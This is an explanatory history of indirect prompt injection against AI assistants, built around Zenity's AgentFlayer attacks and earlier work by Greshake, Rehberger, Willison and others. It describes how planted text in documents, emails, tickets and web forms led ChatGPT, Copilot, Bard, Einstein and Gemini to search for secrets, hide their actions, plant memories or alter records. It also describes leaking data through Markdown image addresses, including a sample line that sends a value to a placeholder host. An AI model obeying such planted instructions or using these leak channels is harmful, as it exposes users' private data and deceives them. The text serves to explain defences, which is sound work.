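# AgentFlayer and the history of indirect prompt injection

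## AgentFlayer and the idea of indirect prompt injection

AgentFlayer is the name that Zenity, which sells security software for AI agents, gave to a set of attacks on the AI assistants that businesses use. Michael Bargury, Zenity's co-founder and chief technology officer, and Tamir Ishay Sharbat, a threat researcher there, presented the attacks in August 2025 at Black Hat USA, a security conference in Las Vegas. In its press release, Zenity (2025) listed six targets: OpenAI's ChatGPT; Copilot Studio, Microsoft's platform for building custom agents; Microsoft 365 Copilot; Google Gemini; Salesforce Einstein, the assistant inside Salesforce's customer-records software; and the code editor Cursor when linked to Jira, a tracker for support and development tickets. In each case, the assistant read text written by an outsider during ordinary work and followed the instructions in it. Security researchers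 call this indirect prompt injection, an idea that was two and a half years old at the time of the presentation.

According to bylines in the archive of Zenity Labs, the company's research arm, Sharbat wrote the posts on Copilot Studio, ChatGPT's links to outside accounts and Salesforce Einstein, Marina Simakov wrote up the Cursor attack, and Dmitry Lozovoy wrote up a further group of attacks on ChatGPT. SC Media's *Black Hat* (2025), a report from the conference, also credits Simakov with the Cursor work that Bargury and Sharbat showed there.

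Some of the attacks were published before they were called AgentFlayer. *A Copilot Studio Story 2* (Sharbat, 2025), published on 7 July, a month before Black Hat, described the theft of customer records from a Copilot Studio agent. A week later, Office 365 for IT Pros' *Copilot Studio Agent Vulnerability to Prompt Injection* (2025) discussed the post under its original title. Simakov's post is dated 1 August, and a 2025 version of her author page at Zenity Labs lists it as "When a Jira Ticket Can Steal Your Secrets". Zenity Labs has since added "AgentFlayer" to the start of both titles. Bargury's summary of the talk, *Pwn the Enterprise*, doesn't use the name. The name covers some months of research, and vendors had already dealt with part of what was found. The timeline in Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* post on Copilot Studio dates Microsoft's fix to 24 April.

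### Prompt injection, direct and indirect

The language model behind a chatbot receives the developer's instructions, the user's request and any attached document as one long piece of text, and produces a continuation of the whole. It cannot reliably distinguish instructions from data. Prompt injection is text that exploits this weakness to make the model follow an attacker's instructions.

Riley Goodside gave the best-known early example of prompt injection in September 2022. He asked GPT-3, then OpenAI's main model, to translate a passage into French. The passage was an instruction to output a mocking phrase instead, and GPT-3 output the phrase. A day later, the software developer Simon Willison named the problem in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* (2022), which starts from Goodside's examples. Others had found the flaw earlier. Preamble's *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure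 of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3* dates the company's private report to OpenAI to 3 May 2022.

Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, an old way of attacking websites. Programs use SQL to give commands to a database. If a website builds those commands by pasting in whatever visitors type, a visitor can type a fragment of SQL and get the database to run it. Hackaday's *What's Old Is New Again* (2022) traces both attacks to user-supplied data being "incorrectly treated as instruction". Programmers can stop SQL injection by sending the command and the visitor's text to the database separately, so that the database never treats the text as a command, but a language model has no such second channel. Four days after coining the term, Willison wrote in *I don't know how to solve prompt injection* (2022) that he knew how to beat SQL injection but had no idea how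 to beat prompt injection reliably.

The comparison with SQL injection also misleads about an attack's effects. Brodt, Feldman and colleagues (2026) point out in *The Promptware Kill Chain* that SQL injection mostly damages the database it reaches, whereas an injected prompt can use every permission and tool the application holds. The outcome of an injected prompt also varies from run to run, unlike that of a database command.

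People often confuse prompt injection with jailbreaking, which is getting a model to do something its safety training or its developer's rules would make it refuse. Brodt and colleagues distinguish jailbreaking from injection, which gets the attacker's instructions into the text the model reads. One attack may need both, but an attacker who only wants the assistant to do something routine, such as searching a folder, may not need a jailbreak. The stakes also differ. In an interview, RedMonk's *Simon Willison on Industry's Tardy Response to the AI Prompt Injection Vulnerability*, Willison separated moderation, which stops a model from producing offensive text, from security, which stops an attacker from making it leak private data.

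In Goodside's example, the person typing was the attacker. In indirect prompt injection, the attacker places the text in content that the model reads on a user's behalf, such as a web page, file, email or ticket, and the user becomes the victim. The danger therefore grows with the amount of outside content an assistant can read and the actions it can then take.

By 2025, two kinds of link had given AI assistants access to more outside data and tools. The first, connectors, let an assistant search a user's outside accounts. Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* post on ChatGPT describes connectors to Google Drive, SharePoint and GitHub, which ChatGPT can use to look up files and pull live data to answer a question. The second, the Model Context Protocol (MCP), is a common standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools and data. A small program called an MCP server sits between the application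 and the tool, so that Cursor, for instance, can fetch Jira tickets when a developer asks about them. Neither kind of link checks whether a file or ticket was written with malicious intent.

### What Greshake and colleagues showed in 2023

The term "indirect prompt injection" comes from *Not what you've signed up for*, by Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2023). They noticed that when an application retrieves outside material, an attacker doesn't need access to the application, only somewhere to leave text that it will read. They compared letting a model process such text to running arbitrary code from a stranger. Until then, most people had pictured a malicious user attacking a chatbot directly, and such a user mostly ends up with a misbehaving chatbot.

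They described four ways of getting the injected text into an application. In passive delivery, the attacker leaves it where the application will find it: on a web page pushed up the search rankings, in a public code repository, or among the documents an assistant searches. In active delivery, the attacker sends it to the target, mainly by email, where a spam filter or personal assistant will process it. In user-driven delivery, the victim enters it, for example by copying text from the attacker's website and pasting it into ChatGPT. The fourth category, hidden injections, is a form of concealment that can be combined with any of the others. A short instruction can make the application fetch a longer one from elsewhere, or the attacker can encode the text or put it in an image. The document that Sharbat prepared for ChatGPT in 2025, with its instructions in tiny white type, was both user-driven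 and hidden.

Greshake and colleagues built a test chat application on OpenAI's models, first text-davinci-003 and then GPT-4. They gave it tools for searching, opening web addresses, reading and sending email, looking up contacts and keeping notes. The tools returned only prepared content and could not affect real systems. The other main target was Microsoft's Bing Chat, a real product. To avoid planting anything on the public web, the researchers put their instructions in invisible comments in local web pages and opened them in Microsoft's Edge browser, where Bing Chat could read the current page from a sidebar. They also tested GitHub Copilot, which completes programmers' code.

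They sorted the possible harms into six classes and ran at least one attack in each:

| Class of harm | Shown on a real product | Shown on the test application |
|---|---|---|
| Information gathering | Bing Chat draws out a user's name and offers a link that carries it | The same attack |
| Fraud | Bing Chat promotes a fake gift card | None |
| Malware | Bing Chat recommends malicious links | An email assistant forwards the injection to the user's contacts |
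| Intrusion | GitHub Copilot picks up instructions from a code package, unreliably | The model fetches new orders from a mock server; an injection survives a reset |
| Manipulated content | Bing Chat gives false summaries, slants political answers and suppresses a newspaper | None |
| Availability | Bing Chat times out, answers without text or corrupts its own searches | None |

In the first attack in the table, the attacker had to spell out little. The planted text told Bing Chat to persuade the user without arousing suspicion and named no technique. One of the researchers, playing a journalist, asked about the next day's weather. Bing Chat answered, asked about plans for the day, moved on to the user's job, and asked whether the journalist wrote under a real name. Once it had a name, it offered a link to an "exclusive" website with a scrambled form of the name in the address. Clicking the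 link would have sent the name to whoever ran the site.

The researchers also found that Bing Chat's filter ended the conversation when a user typed a known jailbreak but let the same kind of text through when it came from a page. In most cases, the injection remained active for the rest of the session. The researchers acknowledged that they did not measure success rates. They offered only informal evidence that the attacks were easy, reporting that they often worked on the first attempt and leaving in their own spelling mistakes to show how easy it was. The attack was weakest against GitHub Copilot, where the injection lost much of its effect inside larger programs.

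Three of the demonstrations anticipate claims that Zenity and others made in 2025, and all three ran only on the test application. The email attack was a computer worm written in ordinary language. The assistant read an incoming message containing an injection, looked through the user's address book and forwarded the message so that other people's assistants would read it too. In the memory attack, the injection made the model save part of the injected text to a store of notes. After the researchers reset the model, it behaved normally until the user asked it to read back the last conversation, which reactivated the injection and made the model talk like a pirate. The attack would not need that request in a product that loads saved memories into every conversation, as ChatGPT later did. In the third attack, an already compromised model fetched new instructions from a mock server each time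 the user asked something, which would give an attacker continuing control.

Greshake and colleagues also wrote that attacks with no human in the loop "could be possible" against assistants that read email, reach personal data and send messages. Sharbat's Copilot Studio attack closely fits that description, including the delivery of stolen records by email. It ran on Microsoft's actual platform, although the agent was Zenity's own replica of one built by the consultancy McKinsey. Greshake and colleagues could not have tried anything like this because they had no access to Microsoft 365 Copilot or to ChatGPT's plugins, an earlier way of linking ChatGPT to other services. They had only anecdotes about injections retrieved from the live web, such as people putting instructions for Bing Chat on their personal pages.

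### How the prediction has fared

Researchers have since attacked real products in most of the ways the 2023 paper could only mock up. Brodt and colleagues reviewed 36 studies and incidents dated between February 2023 and January 2026 and argued that prompt injection has become a way to deliver malware that they call promptware. They divide an attack into seven stages: initial access (the injection), privilege escalation (the jailbreak), reconnaissance, persistence, command and control, lateral movement to other systems or users, and the final harmful action.

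The paper gives different counts of the attacks that pass through four or more stages. The abstract gives at least 21, the introduction gives fifteen, and the rows of the table add up to 22. Those 22 include none of the three attacks from 2023, seven of the twelve from 2024, and fifteen of the 21 from 2025 and January 2026. The introduction's figure matches the count for 2025 and January 2026 alone. The abstract's figure may come from an error in the 2024 count, because the text gives two five-stage attacks for that year and the table gives three. No attack reached six stages.

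The growth is real, but the table makes it look steeper than it was. Brodt and colleagues list the Greshake paper as a three-stage attack on Bing Chat and plugins, and say that no incident in 2023 showed persistence, command and control, or lateral movement. But Greshake and colleagues had shown all three on their test application, and they had not been able to test plugins. The survey also covers selected prominent cases, most of them demonstrations by researchers, so it tracks what researchers have managed to do rather than how often criminals do it.

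The survey lists AgentFlayer at five stages, but uses the name only for Simakov's attack on Cursor. Two of the five stages depend on how Brodt and colleagues define their terms. They count malicious text as persistence if it sits in a stored document until an assistant retrieves it, so a Jira ticket qualifies. They count text passing from one application into another as lateral movement. A poisoned web page that stays online would seem to meet the definition of persistence too, yet they don't list that stage for the 2023 Bing Chat attacks. The number of stages describes an attack's route reasonably well but is a poor measure of its severity.

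The best evidence on what injections people actually plant comes from an April 2026 study, *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, by Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues. They searched about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of the web, covering 1.2 billion addresses on 24.8 million hosts. They looked for 3,963 phrases that suggest an injection and reviewed the matches, partly by hand, to exclude tutorials and news articles. Including some found through Censys and Shodan, two search engines for internet-connected machines, they confirmed 15,387 injections on 11,722 pages. In Common Crawl alone, the rate was about eight pages in a million.

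Only 13 of the 15,387 injections were meant to steal data. The largest group, 8,894, were meant to disrupt whatever AI system read the page, usually by making it output rubbish, and 1,521 were meant to promote a product, source or job candidate. Greshake and colleagues had foreseen both uses, but not how many website owners would use the technique in self-defence. Of the injections, 4,093 told AI systems to leave personal or copyrighted material alone, and 3,096 were meant to unmask bots. Some injections fall into more than one group. In Common Crawl, four in five injections came from the site's own operator.

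These injections rarely worked. Khodayari and colleagues had 13 models summarise pages containing 100 different injections, each page in four formats, for 5,200 trials. The models followed the injections in 81 trials, or 1.6 percent. The highest rate was 8 percent, for small models reading text stripped of all formatting. Commercial closed models followed the injections in 5 of 800 trials. In six trials, a model identified the injection but still followed it.

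Those rates are somewhat reassuring about the open web, but much less so about AgentFlayer. Stock phrases from 54 templates made up 95 percent of the planted texts, while Sharbat and Simakov wrote theirs for one particular assistant and revised them until they worked. In the trials, the model summarised a page and had no tools to misuse. The phrase search would also have missed disguised or non-English injections, so its totals are a lower bound. A crawl of public pages does not reach inboxes, ticket queues or shared drives, where Zenity's attacks began.

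## How stolen data leaves through a Markdown image

When Greshake and colleagues had Bing Chat draw out a journalist's name, the name was not sent until the user clicked a link. A Markdown image removes the need for that click. Chat assistants write their answers in Markdown, a simple notation for formatting text in which two asterisks on either side of a word make it bold. An exclamation mark, followed by a label in square brackets and a web address in parentheses, inserts an image.

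Suppose a user tells an assistant that her favourite colour is blue, then asks it to summarise a web page. An attacker has left instructions on the page. The model follows them and ends its summary with this code:

`![cat](pictures.example/cat.png?colour=blue)`

To show the picture in place of the code, the chat window requests the address from the attacker's server. Everything after the question mark is extra information for the server, which websites often use for search terms. This server ignores it and returns the cat, but records the full address in its log, as web servers commonly do. The attacker opens the log and reads "blue". The user sees a cat, or nothing if the image is a single transparent pixel.

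The model has only written text. The request comes from the user's own browser or app, which loads images automatically.

Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found the trick at the end of March 2023. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, found it independently a few days later, as he explained in *ChatGPT Plugins* (2023). In the attack Samoilenko described in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, a script on the attacker's website added the injection to whatever a visitor copied, and the visitor then pasted it into ChatGPT. The attacker could use the image to steal code that ChatGPT had just corrected, and the injection could make ChatGPT add a new image to every later answer in the chat. The results varied between attempts. Samoilenko found it easy to steal earlier prompts or code, but very difficult to steal passwords or API keys,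 the secret codes that programs use to log in to a service. He advised OpenAI to stop showing Markdown images. Willison (2023) drew attention to the work on 14 April in a post with the same title as Samoilenko's.

Rehberger had reported the problem to OpenAI on 9 April. In his version, the user didn't have to paste anything, because a ChatGPT plugin could pick up the injection from a web page or a video transcript. OpenAI replied that showing images was a feature and that it planned no changes.

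### Bing Chat and Bard

Microsoft reacted differently. Rehberger had shown that a comment or advertisement on a web page could make Bing Chat send out a secret from elsewhere on the same page. According to Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, he reported this on 8 April 2023 and Microsoft told him of a fix on 15 June. Part of the fix was a Content Security Policy, a website's list of the places from which the browser may load its content. The list now allowed images from only a few Bing addresses.

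Google's chatbot Bard, now Gemini, already had such a list when Rehberger turned to it that autumn. Google had just given Bard access to users' Gmail, Docs and Drive. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes the attack, which Rehberger developed with Joseph Thacker and with Kai Greshake, who co-wrote the 2023 paper. He put the injection in a Google Doc. Anyone can share a Google Doc with a stranger who hasn't asked for it, so a victim might bring it into a chat just by searching their own files with Bard.

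Bard followed the instructions and wrote the image code, but the browser refused to load an image from Rehberger's server. The permitted list included every address ending in google.com or googleusercontent.com, though, and Google lets users run their own programs at some of those addresses. Apps Script, a tool for automating Google's office software, gives each program a web address on a Google domain. Rehberger used it to write a small program that copied the data in any incoming request into a document he controlled, and he found a setting that let the program accept requests without a login. In the demonstration, a user chatted with Bard and then asked about the shared document. Bard put the first 20 words of the conversation into an image address on a Google domain, the browser loaded the image, and the words appeared in Rehberger's document. He needed ten attempts and some worked examples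 to get Bard to put the data in the right place, which other chatbots hadn't needed.

The stolen text was already in the chat, although Bard could also have searched the user's email. Rehberger reported the flaw on 19 September 2023, and Google confirmed a fix a month later. The list of permitted domains hadn't changed and images still loaded, so he supposed that Google had started to filter data out of image addresses.

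### Attacks in which the model fetched more data

Rehberger had already made ChatGPT fetch private data itself in a May 2023 demonstration. He had ChatGPT open a malicious page through WebPilot, a browsing plugin. ChatGPT then used a second plugin, from the automation company Zapier, to retrieve the user's latest email. It summarised the email, added the summary to a URL and had WebPilot open that URL, so the data left through a browsing request rather than an image. Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained* sets out the steps. In *Let ChatGPT visit a website and have your email stolen*, Willison called the demonstration the first working proof he had seen of such a theft through plugins. Zapier responded by making users confirm such actions.

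That September, Rehberger combined plugins with images to get around the limit on how much data a web address can hold. Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* describes how an injection made ChatGPT use a plugin to turn the whole conversation into a document, diagram or video stored online. The image's address then only had to include a link to that file.

Rehberger's attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot also made the model search for the data. Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Exposes User Data Risks* dates the post describing it to 26 August 2024. A malicious email or shared document made Copilot look for other emails and bring sales figures and Slack login codes into the chat. Microsoft had already closed the image route, so Rehberger had Copilot write the stolen text in invisible characters inside an ordinary-looking link, which the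 user had to click. According to the timeline in Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot*, Microsoft initially closed his report on the invisible characters as low severity, then opened a case after he sent the complete attack in February 2024. Microsoft never told him how it had fixed the problem.

By August 2024, Rehberger had shown that an attacker's instructions could make models fetch private data, and that images could send data out without a click, but none of these attacks did both.

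### OpenAI's url_safe check

According to Embrace The Red's slides, *HackSpaceCon New Important Instructions*, Bing Chat, Claude, Bard, Discord and two cloud services had fixed the image problem by November 2023. The slides listed ChatGPT as "won't fix".

The next month, OpenAI changed course and had ChatGPT's web page send each image address to url_safe, a check on OpenAI's servers, and load the image only if the check found the address safe. Anyone can read a Content Security Policy in their browser, but OpenAI didn't publish the rules behind url_safe. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* reports that in tests on the first day, the check rejected an image address that contained an email address. But when Rehberger made one image address for each letter and digit, nine of the 36 passed, for no reason he could see. He was able to use these to send himself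 the word "hi", one letter per image.

The check also protected only the web version, because each app had to call url_safe itself and the iPhone app didn't. In 2024, OpenAI released its Android and Mac apps with the same flaw. It had also given ChatGPT a memory that carries over into new conversations. Rehberger combined the missing check with the memory feature in an attack he called SpAIware. A malicious web page made ChatGPT save an instruction as a memory. From then on, the Mac app added an invisible image to its answers, which sent Rehberger's server everything the user typed and everything ChatGPT replied. Greshake and colleagues had made injected instructions persist like this only in their test application.

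OpenAI closed Rehberger's May 2024 report on false memories as a matter of model safety rather than security. In June he sent a demonstration of the full data theft, and OpenAI fixed the Mac app in September. According to Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*, the fix stopped data from leaving through images, but a web page could still plant a memory.

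ChatGPT could also contact a server by opening a web address. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (Schwartzman, 2024) showed that an attacker could steal personal data this way because ChatGPT would open any address at the user's request, a feature that Claude, Bing and Gemini had disabled.

### The trusted storage domain

In October 2024, Rehberger reported to OpenAI that url_safe treated windows.net as safe, a domain where Microsoft's cloud customers store files. Anyone can open a storage account there, upload an image and read the log of requests for it. He had found a similar problem with apache.org. His demonstration stole the summary of recent conversations that ChatGPT keeps in its hidden instructions, and he noted that saved memories could be stolen the same way. The storage route still worked when he published the finding, which Willison's *The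 Summer of Johann* dates to 1 August 2025. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* adds that he had asked OpenAI about a fix several times in the preceding month and received no update.

Zenity presented its ChatGPT attack days later. Sharbat's first version failed because url_safe rejected the image's address, which belonged to a service for testing web requests. He then moved the image to Microsoft's cloud storage, where the log recorded the API keys that ChatGPT had found in the victim's Google Drive.

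In its post, Zenity Labs credits Rehberger's SpAIware work for the image channel but says only "we found a bypass" about the storage domain. It doesn't mention Rehberger's report or claim independent discovery. Zenity may well have found the gap alone, since a researcher with a Microsoft cloud account could test it in minutes. Rehberger had also presented url_safe bypasses at Black Hat Europe in 2024, though he doesn't specify which ones in his later account. He reported the storage domain bypass ten months before Zenity's talk and published it first.

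### Why trusted domains leak

OpenAI tightened url_safe around August 2025, which stopped these attacks. In November, Tenable's *HackedGPT* described another way around the check. url_safe always accepted bing.com, and links in Bing's search results go to a bing.com address that forwards to the actual site. Bing's links can't be altered, so Tenable couldn't add data to them. Instead, it got its own test pages into Bing's index, one for each letter of the alphabet, and had ChatGPT load their links in the order that spelled out the stolen text.

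A domain is safe to permit only if outsiders cannot read the requests sent to it. Google, Microsoft and Bing domains were on the lists because they are reputable, but on large platforms an outsider can often read requests by renting storage, running a program or getting a link that forwards elsewhere. A company's own servers may have the same weakness. The attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot in *EchoLeak* (2025) used a relay that the permitted list allowed. In June 2026, researchers at Varonis disclosed SearchLeak, in which a permitted Bing address passed Copilot data on to the attacker. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* places both in the family of attacks that Rehberger has demonstrated since 2023. Microsoft rated SearchLeak critical and patched it, according to CPO Magazine's *“SearchLeak” Copilot Vulnerability Chain*.

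Short lists of allowed addresses can still work well. *Silent Egress* (2026) tested an AI agent that could contact only three addresses belonging to its own company and one harmless example site. The list blocked the leaks, whereas putting outside text between tags that marked it as untrusted had no measurable benefit. One reason, according to *The Framing Gap* (2026), is that a list of destinations doesn't have to recognise the secret, while a filter that looks for secrets in outgoing data fails if the attacker has the model encode them. But a short list makes an assistant less useful if it needs to reach many destinations. Four addresses may be enough for a company's internal agent, but not for ChatGPT, which people use to read the whole web.

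### One address for each letter

After ShadowLeak, an earlier attack by the security company Radware, OpenAI also stopped ChatGPT from changing any address it was given, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*. Under this restriction, ChatGPT could not have added "blue" to the address of the cat in the opening example.

Zvika Babo of Radware bypassed the ban with an attack called ZombieAgent. The injection supplied a complete address for each letter, each digit and the space, and ChatGPT opened them one after another. Babo also numbered versions of each address so that the server could put the characters in order. Most of the attack didn't involve images. Radware's *ZombieAgent* concentrates on requests made by OpenAI's own servers, and calls the Markdown image version less reliable and easier to block. Babo reported the attack on 26 September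 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December.

Six weeks later, OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) set out a stricter rule. OpenAI concedes that lists of trusted sites aren't enough, because trusted sites can forward a request elsewhere and strict lists produce so many warnings that people stop reading them. ChatGPT now checks the exact address against an index of addresses that OpenAI's crawler has found on the public web. The crawler has no access to anyone's conversations. If the address is in the index, ChatGPT may load it automatically. If it isn't, as with an address that contains freshly stolen text, ChatGPT looks for another source or warns the user first.

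The rule makes theft much harder, but an attacker can still leak data through the choice of address. An attacker could publish pictures of a blue cat, a red cat and a green cat, wait for the crawler to index all three, and have ChatGPT reveal the user's favourite colour by which picture it loads. Choosing one address out of *N* conveys log₂ *N* bits. With 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, a request carries about 5.2 bits, and a 20-character key takes 20 requests. With 1,296 addresses, one for each pair of characters, it takes ten. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* points out that a large blog probably has enough indexed pages already, and that OpenAI's technical paper acknowledges the problem. Rehberger suggested stopping the agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, which would make repeated letters harder to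 send.

He was also concerned that some of OpenAI's developers might not know about the check and would build features without it. PromptArmor found such a case. An application built on OpenAI's models had blocked an answer containing a malicious image, but when someone opened the conversation in OpenAI's own log viewer, the viewer loaded the image and sent out the customer's data. *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection* (2026) reports that ChatGPT leaked an invented birthday in a web address that its web tool opened. The log is from 3 February 2026, six days after OpenAI's post. The study offers this as a proof of concept, without a success rate, but the stricter rule should have prevented it. In May 2026, The Hacker News (2026) reported Permiso Security's finding that ChatGPT still fetched images from outside pages it had summarised. This disclosed the user's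 IP address and browser details, which any request reveals, but not the contents of the chat.

OpenAI now treats the check as one of several defenses. If ChatGPT is about to send a third party something it learned in a conversation, it either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation or blocks the request, according to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026). The same protection covers OpenAI's browser, Atlas, and its Deep Research agent. Rehberger has come to a similar view. In Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, he calls the outward channel the only part of such a system that anyone can realistically control.

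The bluntest measure is Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting close to what Samoilenko recommended in 2023. It turns off images in ordinary answers and limits browsing to stored copies of pages. OpenAI announced it for organisations in February in *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) and extended it to personal accounts in June. On the help page, *Lockdown Mode*, OpenAI warns that data may still escape through connected apps. In managed workspaces the administrator decides which apps stay on, and OpenAI advises against allowing an app to write anything an attacker might be able to see.

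## The lethal trifecta, tested on the ChatGPT and Salesforce attacks

Lockdown Mode still lets ChatGPT read a stranger's text and a user's private files, and restricts only its ways of sending data out. Simon Willison had set out the reasoning for this kind of defence in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (June 2025). An agent has what he called the "lethal trifecta" if it combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally. He argued that an attacker can easily trick any such agent into handing over the data.

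### Willison's argument

Willison starts from the weakness behind all prompt injection, that models follow instructions wherever they appear. He thought there was a "very good chance" that a model would obey planted text.

Willison then considered filters, such as telling the model to ignore planted instructions or buying a product that detects them. These stop some attacks, but an attacker can phrase the same instruction in endless ways. Vendors often advertise that their products catch 95 percent of attacks, which he called "very much a failing grade" in web security. A bug that appears in one case out of twenty is normally a nuisance, but an attacker will search for that case and reuse it.

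If a model may follow an attacker's instructions and no filter reliably prevents it, safety depends on what the model can do once it follows them. An attacker can use the model to steal data if it has access to private data, reads untrusted content that can carry the attacker's instructions, and has a channel for sending the data out. Removing any one of these conditions prevents the theft.

Willison had come close to describing the trifecta in November 2023. Commenting on Embrace The Red's attack on Google Bard, he called such attacks inevitable whenever a system combines private data with untrusted inputs. He described the image that carried the data out, but didn't list an outward channel as a condition. Adding that condition gave developers something they could realistically remove. The other two are harder to remove, because people connect an assistant to their email so that it can read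 private messages, many of them from outsiders. The addition also narrowed the warning to data theft.

By mid-2025, Willison could list attacks of this kind on more than a dozen products. The vendors had fixed nearly all of them promptly, usually by closing the channel that let data out. MCP worried him because it lets users assemble the combination themselves. Someone might install one MCP server that reads company files, another that reads public web pages and a third that sends messages, and no vendor can check what they do together.

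Sometimes a single server is enough for an attack. In *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, Willison describes one that Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner found in GitHub's official MCP server. They filed a malicious issue, GitHub's term for a bug report or request, in a public code repository. When the repository's owner asked Claude to look at the issues, Claude read the owner's private repositories and published their names in a proposed code change that anyone could see. In a similar attack on the database service Supabase, the agent copied secrets into a support ticket that the attacker could read. Supabase's read-only setting would have prevented this, because the agent needed write access to leak the secrets.

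### The theft of keys from Google Drive

Zenity's ChatGPT attack fits the trifecta closely. The untrusted content is an ordinary-looking document in which the attacker has hidden instructions in tiny white type. The victim uploads it to ChatGPT and asks for a summary. Zenity Labs points out that a malicious employee could hide instructions in every shared document they can access, greatly increasing the odds that a colleague uploads one.

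In the hidden text, the attacker instructs ChatGPT to drop the summary and search the victim's connected Google Drive for API keys, which are the private data in the trifecta. The attacker adds a cover story about urgent work, because ChatGPT tends to avoid handling credentials, and tells it not to mention the search. ChatGPT then puts the keys it finds in the address of a Markdown image, which is the outward channel.

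The victim may not need to upload the file. The Decoder's *Agent-based AI systems face growing threats from zero-click and one-click exploits* describes a version in which the attacker shares the document to the victim's Drive, and a routine question about a meeting leads ChatGPT to it. The Drive then holds both the private data and the untrusted content, so a user could not separate the two by choosing which connectors to turn on.

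OpenAI's url_safe check targeted the outward channel and blocked Sharbat's first attempt. ChatGPT's tendency to avoid handling credentials removes none of the three conditions and only makes the model less likely to follow an attacker's instructions. Bargury calls such defences "soft boundaries", which include training, statistical filters and written instructions to the model. A "hard boundary" makes an action technically impossible, for example by blocking an image from loading. According to The Decoder, Zenity complained that vendors often relax hard boundaries under competitive pressure because they limit what a product can do.

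*Pwn the Enterprise* records a $1,111 bounty from OpenAI and lists the attack as fixed, explaining that the injection Zenity used no longer works. Taken literally, this means a soft boundary now stops one particular text. The tightening of url_safe around the same time mattered more, because it closed the storage route regardless of the injection's wording. Users could still upload strangers' files and connect their own Drives.

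### Attacks that send nothing out

Two more of Zenity's ChatGPT demonstrations sent no data out. In both, the attacker planted a memory, as Rehberger had done with SpAIware in 2024, but used it to change ChatGPT's advice rather than to copy the conversation. One memory made ChatGPT recommend a malicious software library when the victim asked for code. The other made it try to persuade the victim to do something foolish. ChatGPT met all three conditions of the trifecta at the time, but removing its access to private files and every way of sending data out would not have prevented either attack.

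The Salesforce attack starts with the web forms companies use to collect customer enquiries, hundreds of which Zenity found through Google searches. Salesforce can turn each enquiry into a case, a record for staff to deal with. The attacker submits cases containing hidden instructions. When a sales representative asks Einstein about the latest cases, Einstein reads them and replaces every contact's email address with one on the attacker's domain. The new addresses contain the old ones in coded form, so the attacker can tell whom each message was meant for and forward it. Only customers who had enabled a particular optional action were vulnerable. Salesforce closed Zenity's report without giving a date for a fix, but later told SecurityWeek that it had fixed the flaw on 11 July 2025, The Decoder reports.

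Blocking every outgoing request from Einstein would not have helped, because customer data reaches the attacker later, when employees write to the altered addresses. If this counted as a delayed outward channel, nearly any permission to edit a record would count as communication, and developers could no longer use the condition to decide what to remove.

Noma Security published ForcedLeak, an attack on Salesforce's Agentforce, in September 2025. It also began with a web form, but it sent customers' details out through an image on an expired domain that Salesforce still trusted. Salesforce corrected its list of trusted domains and restricted the links its agent could produce. Those measures stop data from leaving through the image, but they would not stop an attacker from altering contact records.

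The Gemini demonstration needed even less, since Gemini sent nothing out and changed no records. An attacker sends the victim an email or calendar invitation containing instructions tied to a question the victim is likely to ask. In the demonstration, the user asked for a supplier's bank details and Gemini gave the attacker's instead. Any loss would come when the user paid the wrong account. Greshake and colleagues had shown the same kind of harm in 2023 when they made Bing Chat give false summaries. *Pwn the Enterprise* lists the Gemini report as closed after more than 90 days and mentions no fix.

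These attacks are consistent with Willison's claim that the three conditions are enough for theft. He didn't claim that an agent lacking one of them is safe from everything else, and the attacks show the danger of using the trifecta as a general safety checklist. Einstein and Gemini would both have counted as risky under his looser 2023 wording, which didn't mention an outward channel.

### Meta's Agents Rule of Two

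Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), published on 31 October, widened the outward channel to include changes of state, meaning any action that alters something, such as editing a record or making a booking. Within one session, an agent should have no more than two of these properties:

- [A] it can process untrustworthy inputs
- [B] it can access sensitive systems or private data
- [C] it can change state or communicate externally

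An agent that needs all three should not work unsupervised. A person or some other reliable check must approve its actions. Meta modelled the rule on the trifecta and on a 2019 guideline for Google's Chromium browser, which tells programmers not to combine untrustworthy input, an unsafe programming language and high privilege.

Meta's example is an assistant that manages an inbox. The developer could let it read only messages from trusted senders, keep it away from real data, or let it send mail only to trusted recipients or after a person has checked the draft. An agent's permissions can also change during a session. For example, it could browse the web first, then lose the ability to communicate before it opens internal systems.

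The table shows what each of Zenity's attacks actually used.

| Attack | Untrusted content | Private data or sensitive system | Outward channel | Change of state |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT, stolen keys | Document | Google Drive | Image request | None |
| ChatGPT, planted memory | Attacker's text | Not needed | None | Saved memory |
| Salesforce Einstein | Customer case | Contact records | None | Altered addresses |
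| Gemini, false bank details | Email or invitation | Not needed | None | None |

The rule covers the Salesforce attack, since Einstein read outsiders' text, had access to customer records and could edit them. It doesn't cover the Gemini attack, because an assistant that reads an inbox but can't send or change anything has only two of the three properties. Meta acknowledges this gap and classes misinformation in an agent's answer as a "lower consequence" outcome, which is hard to accept when the misinformation is the account number for a payment.

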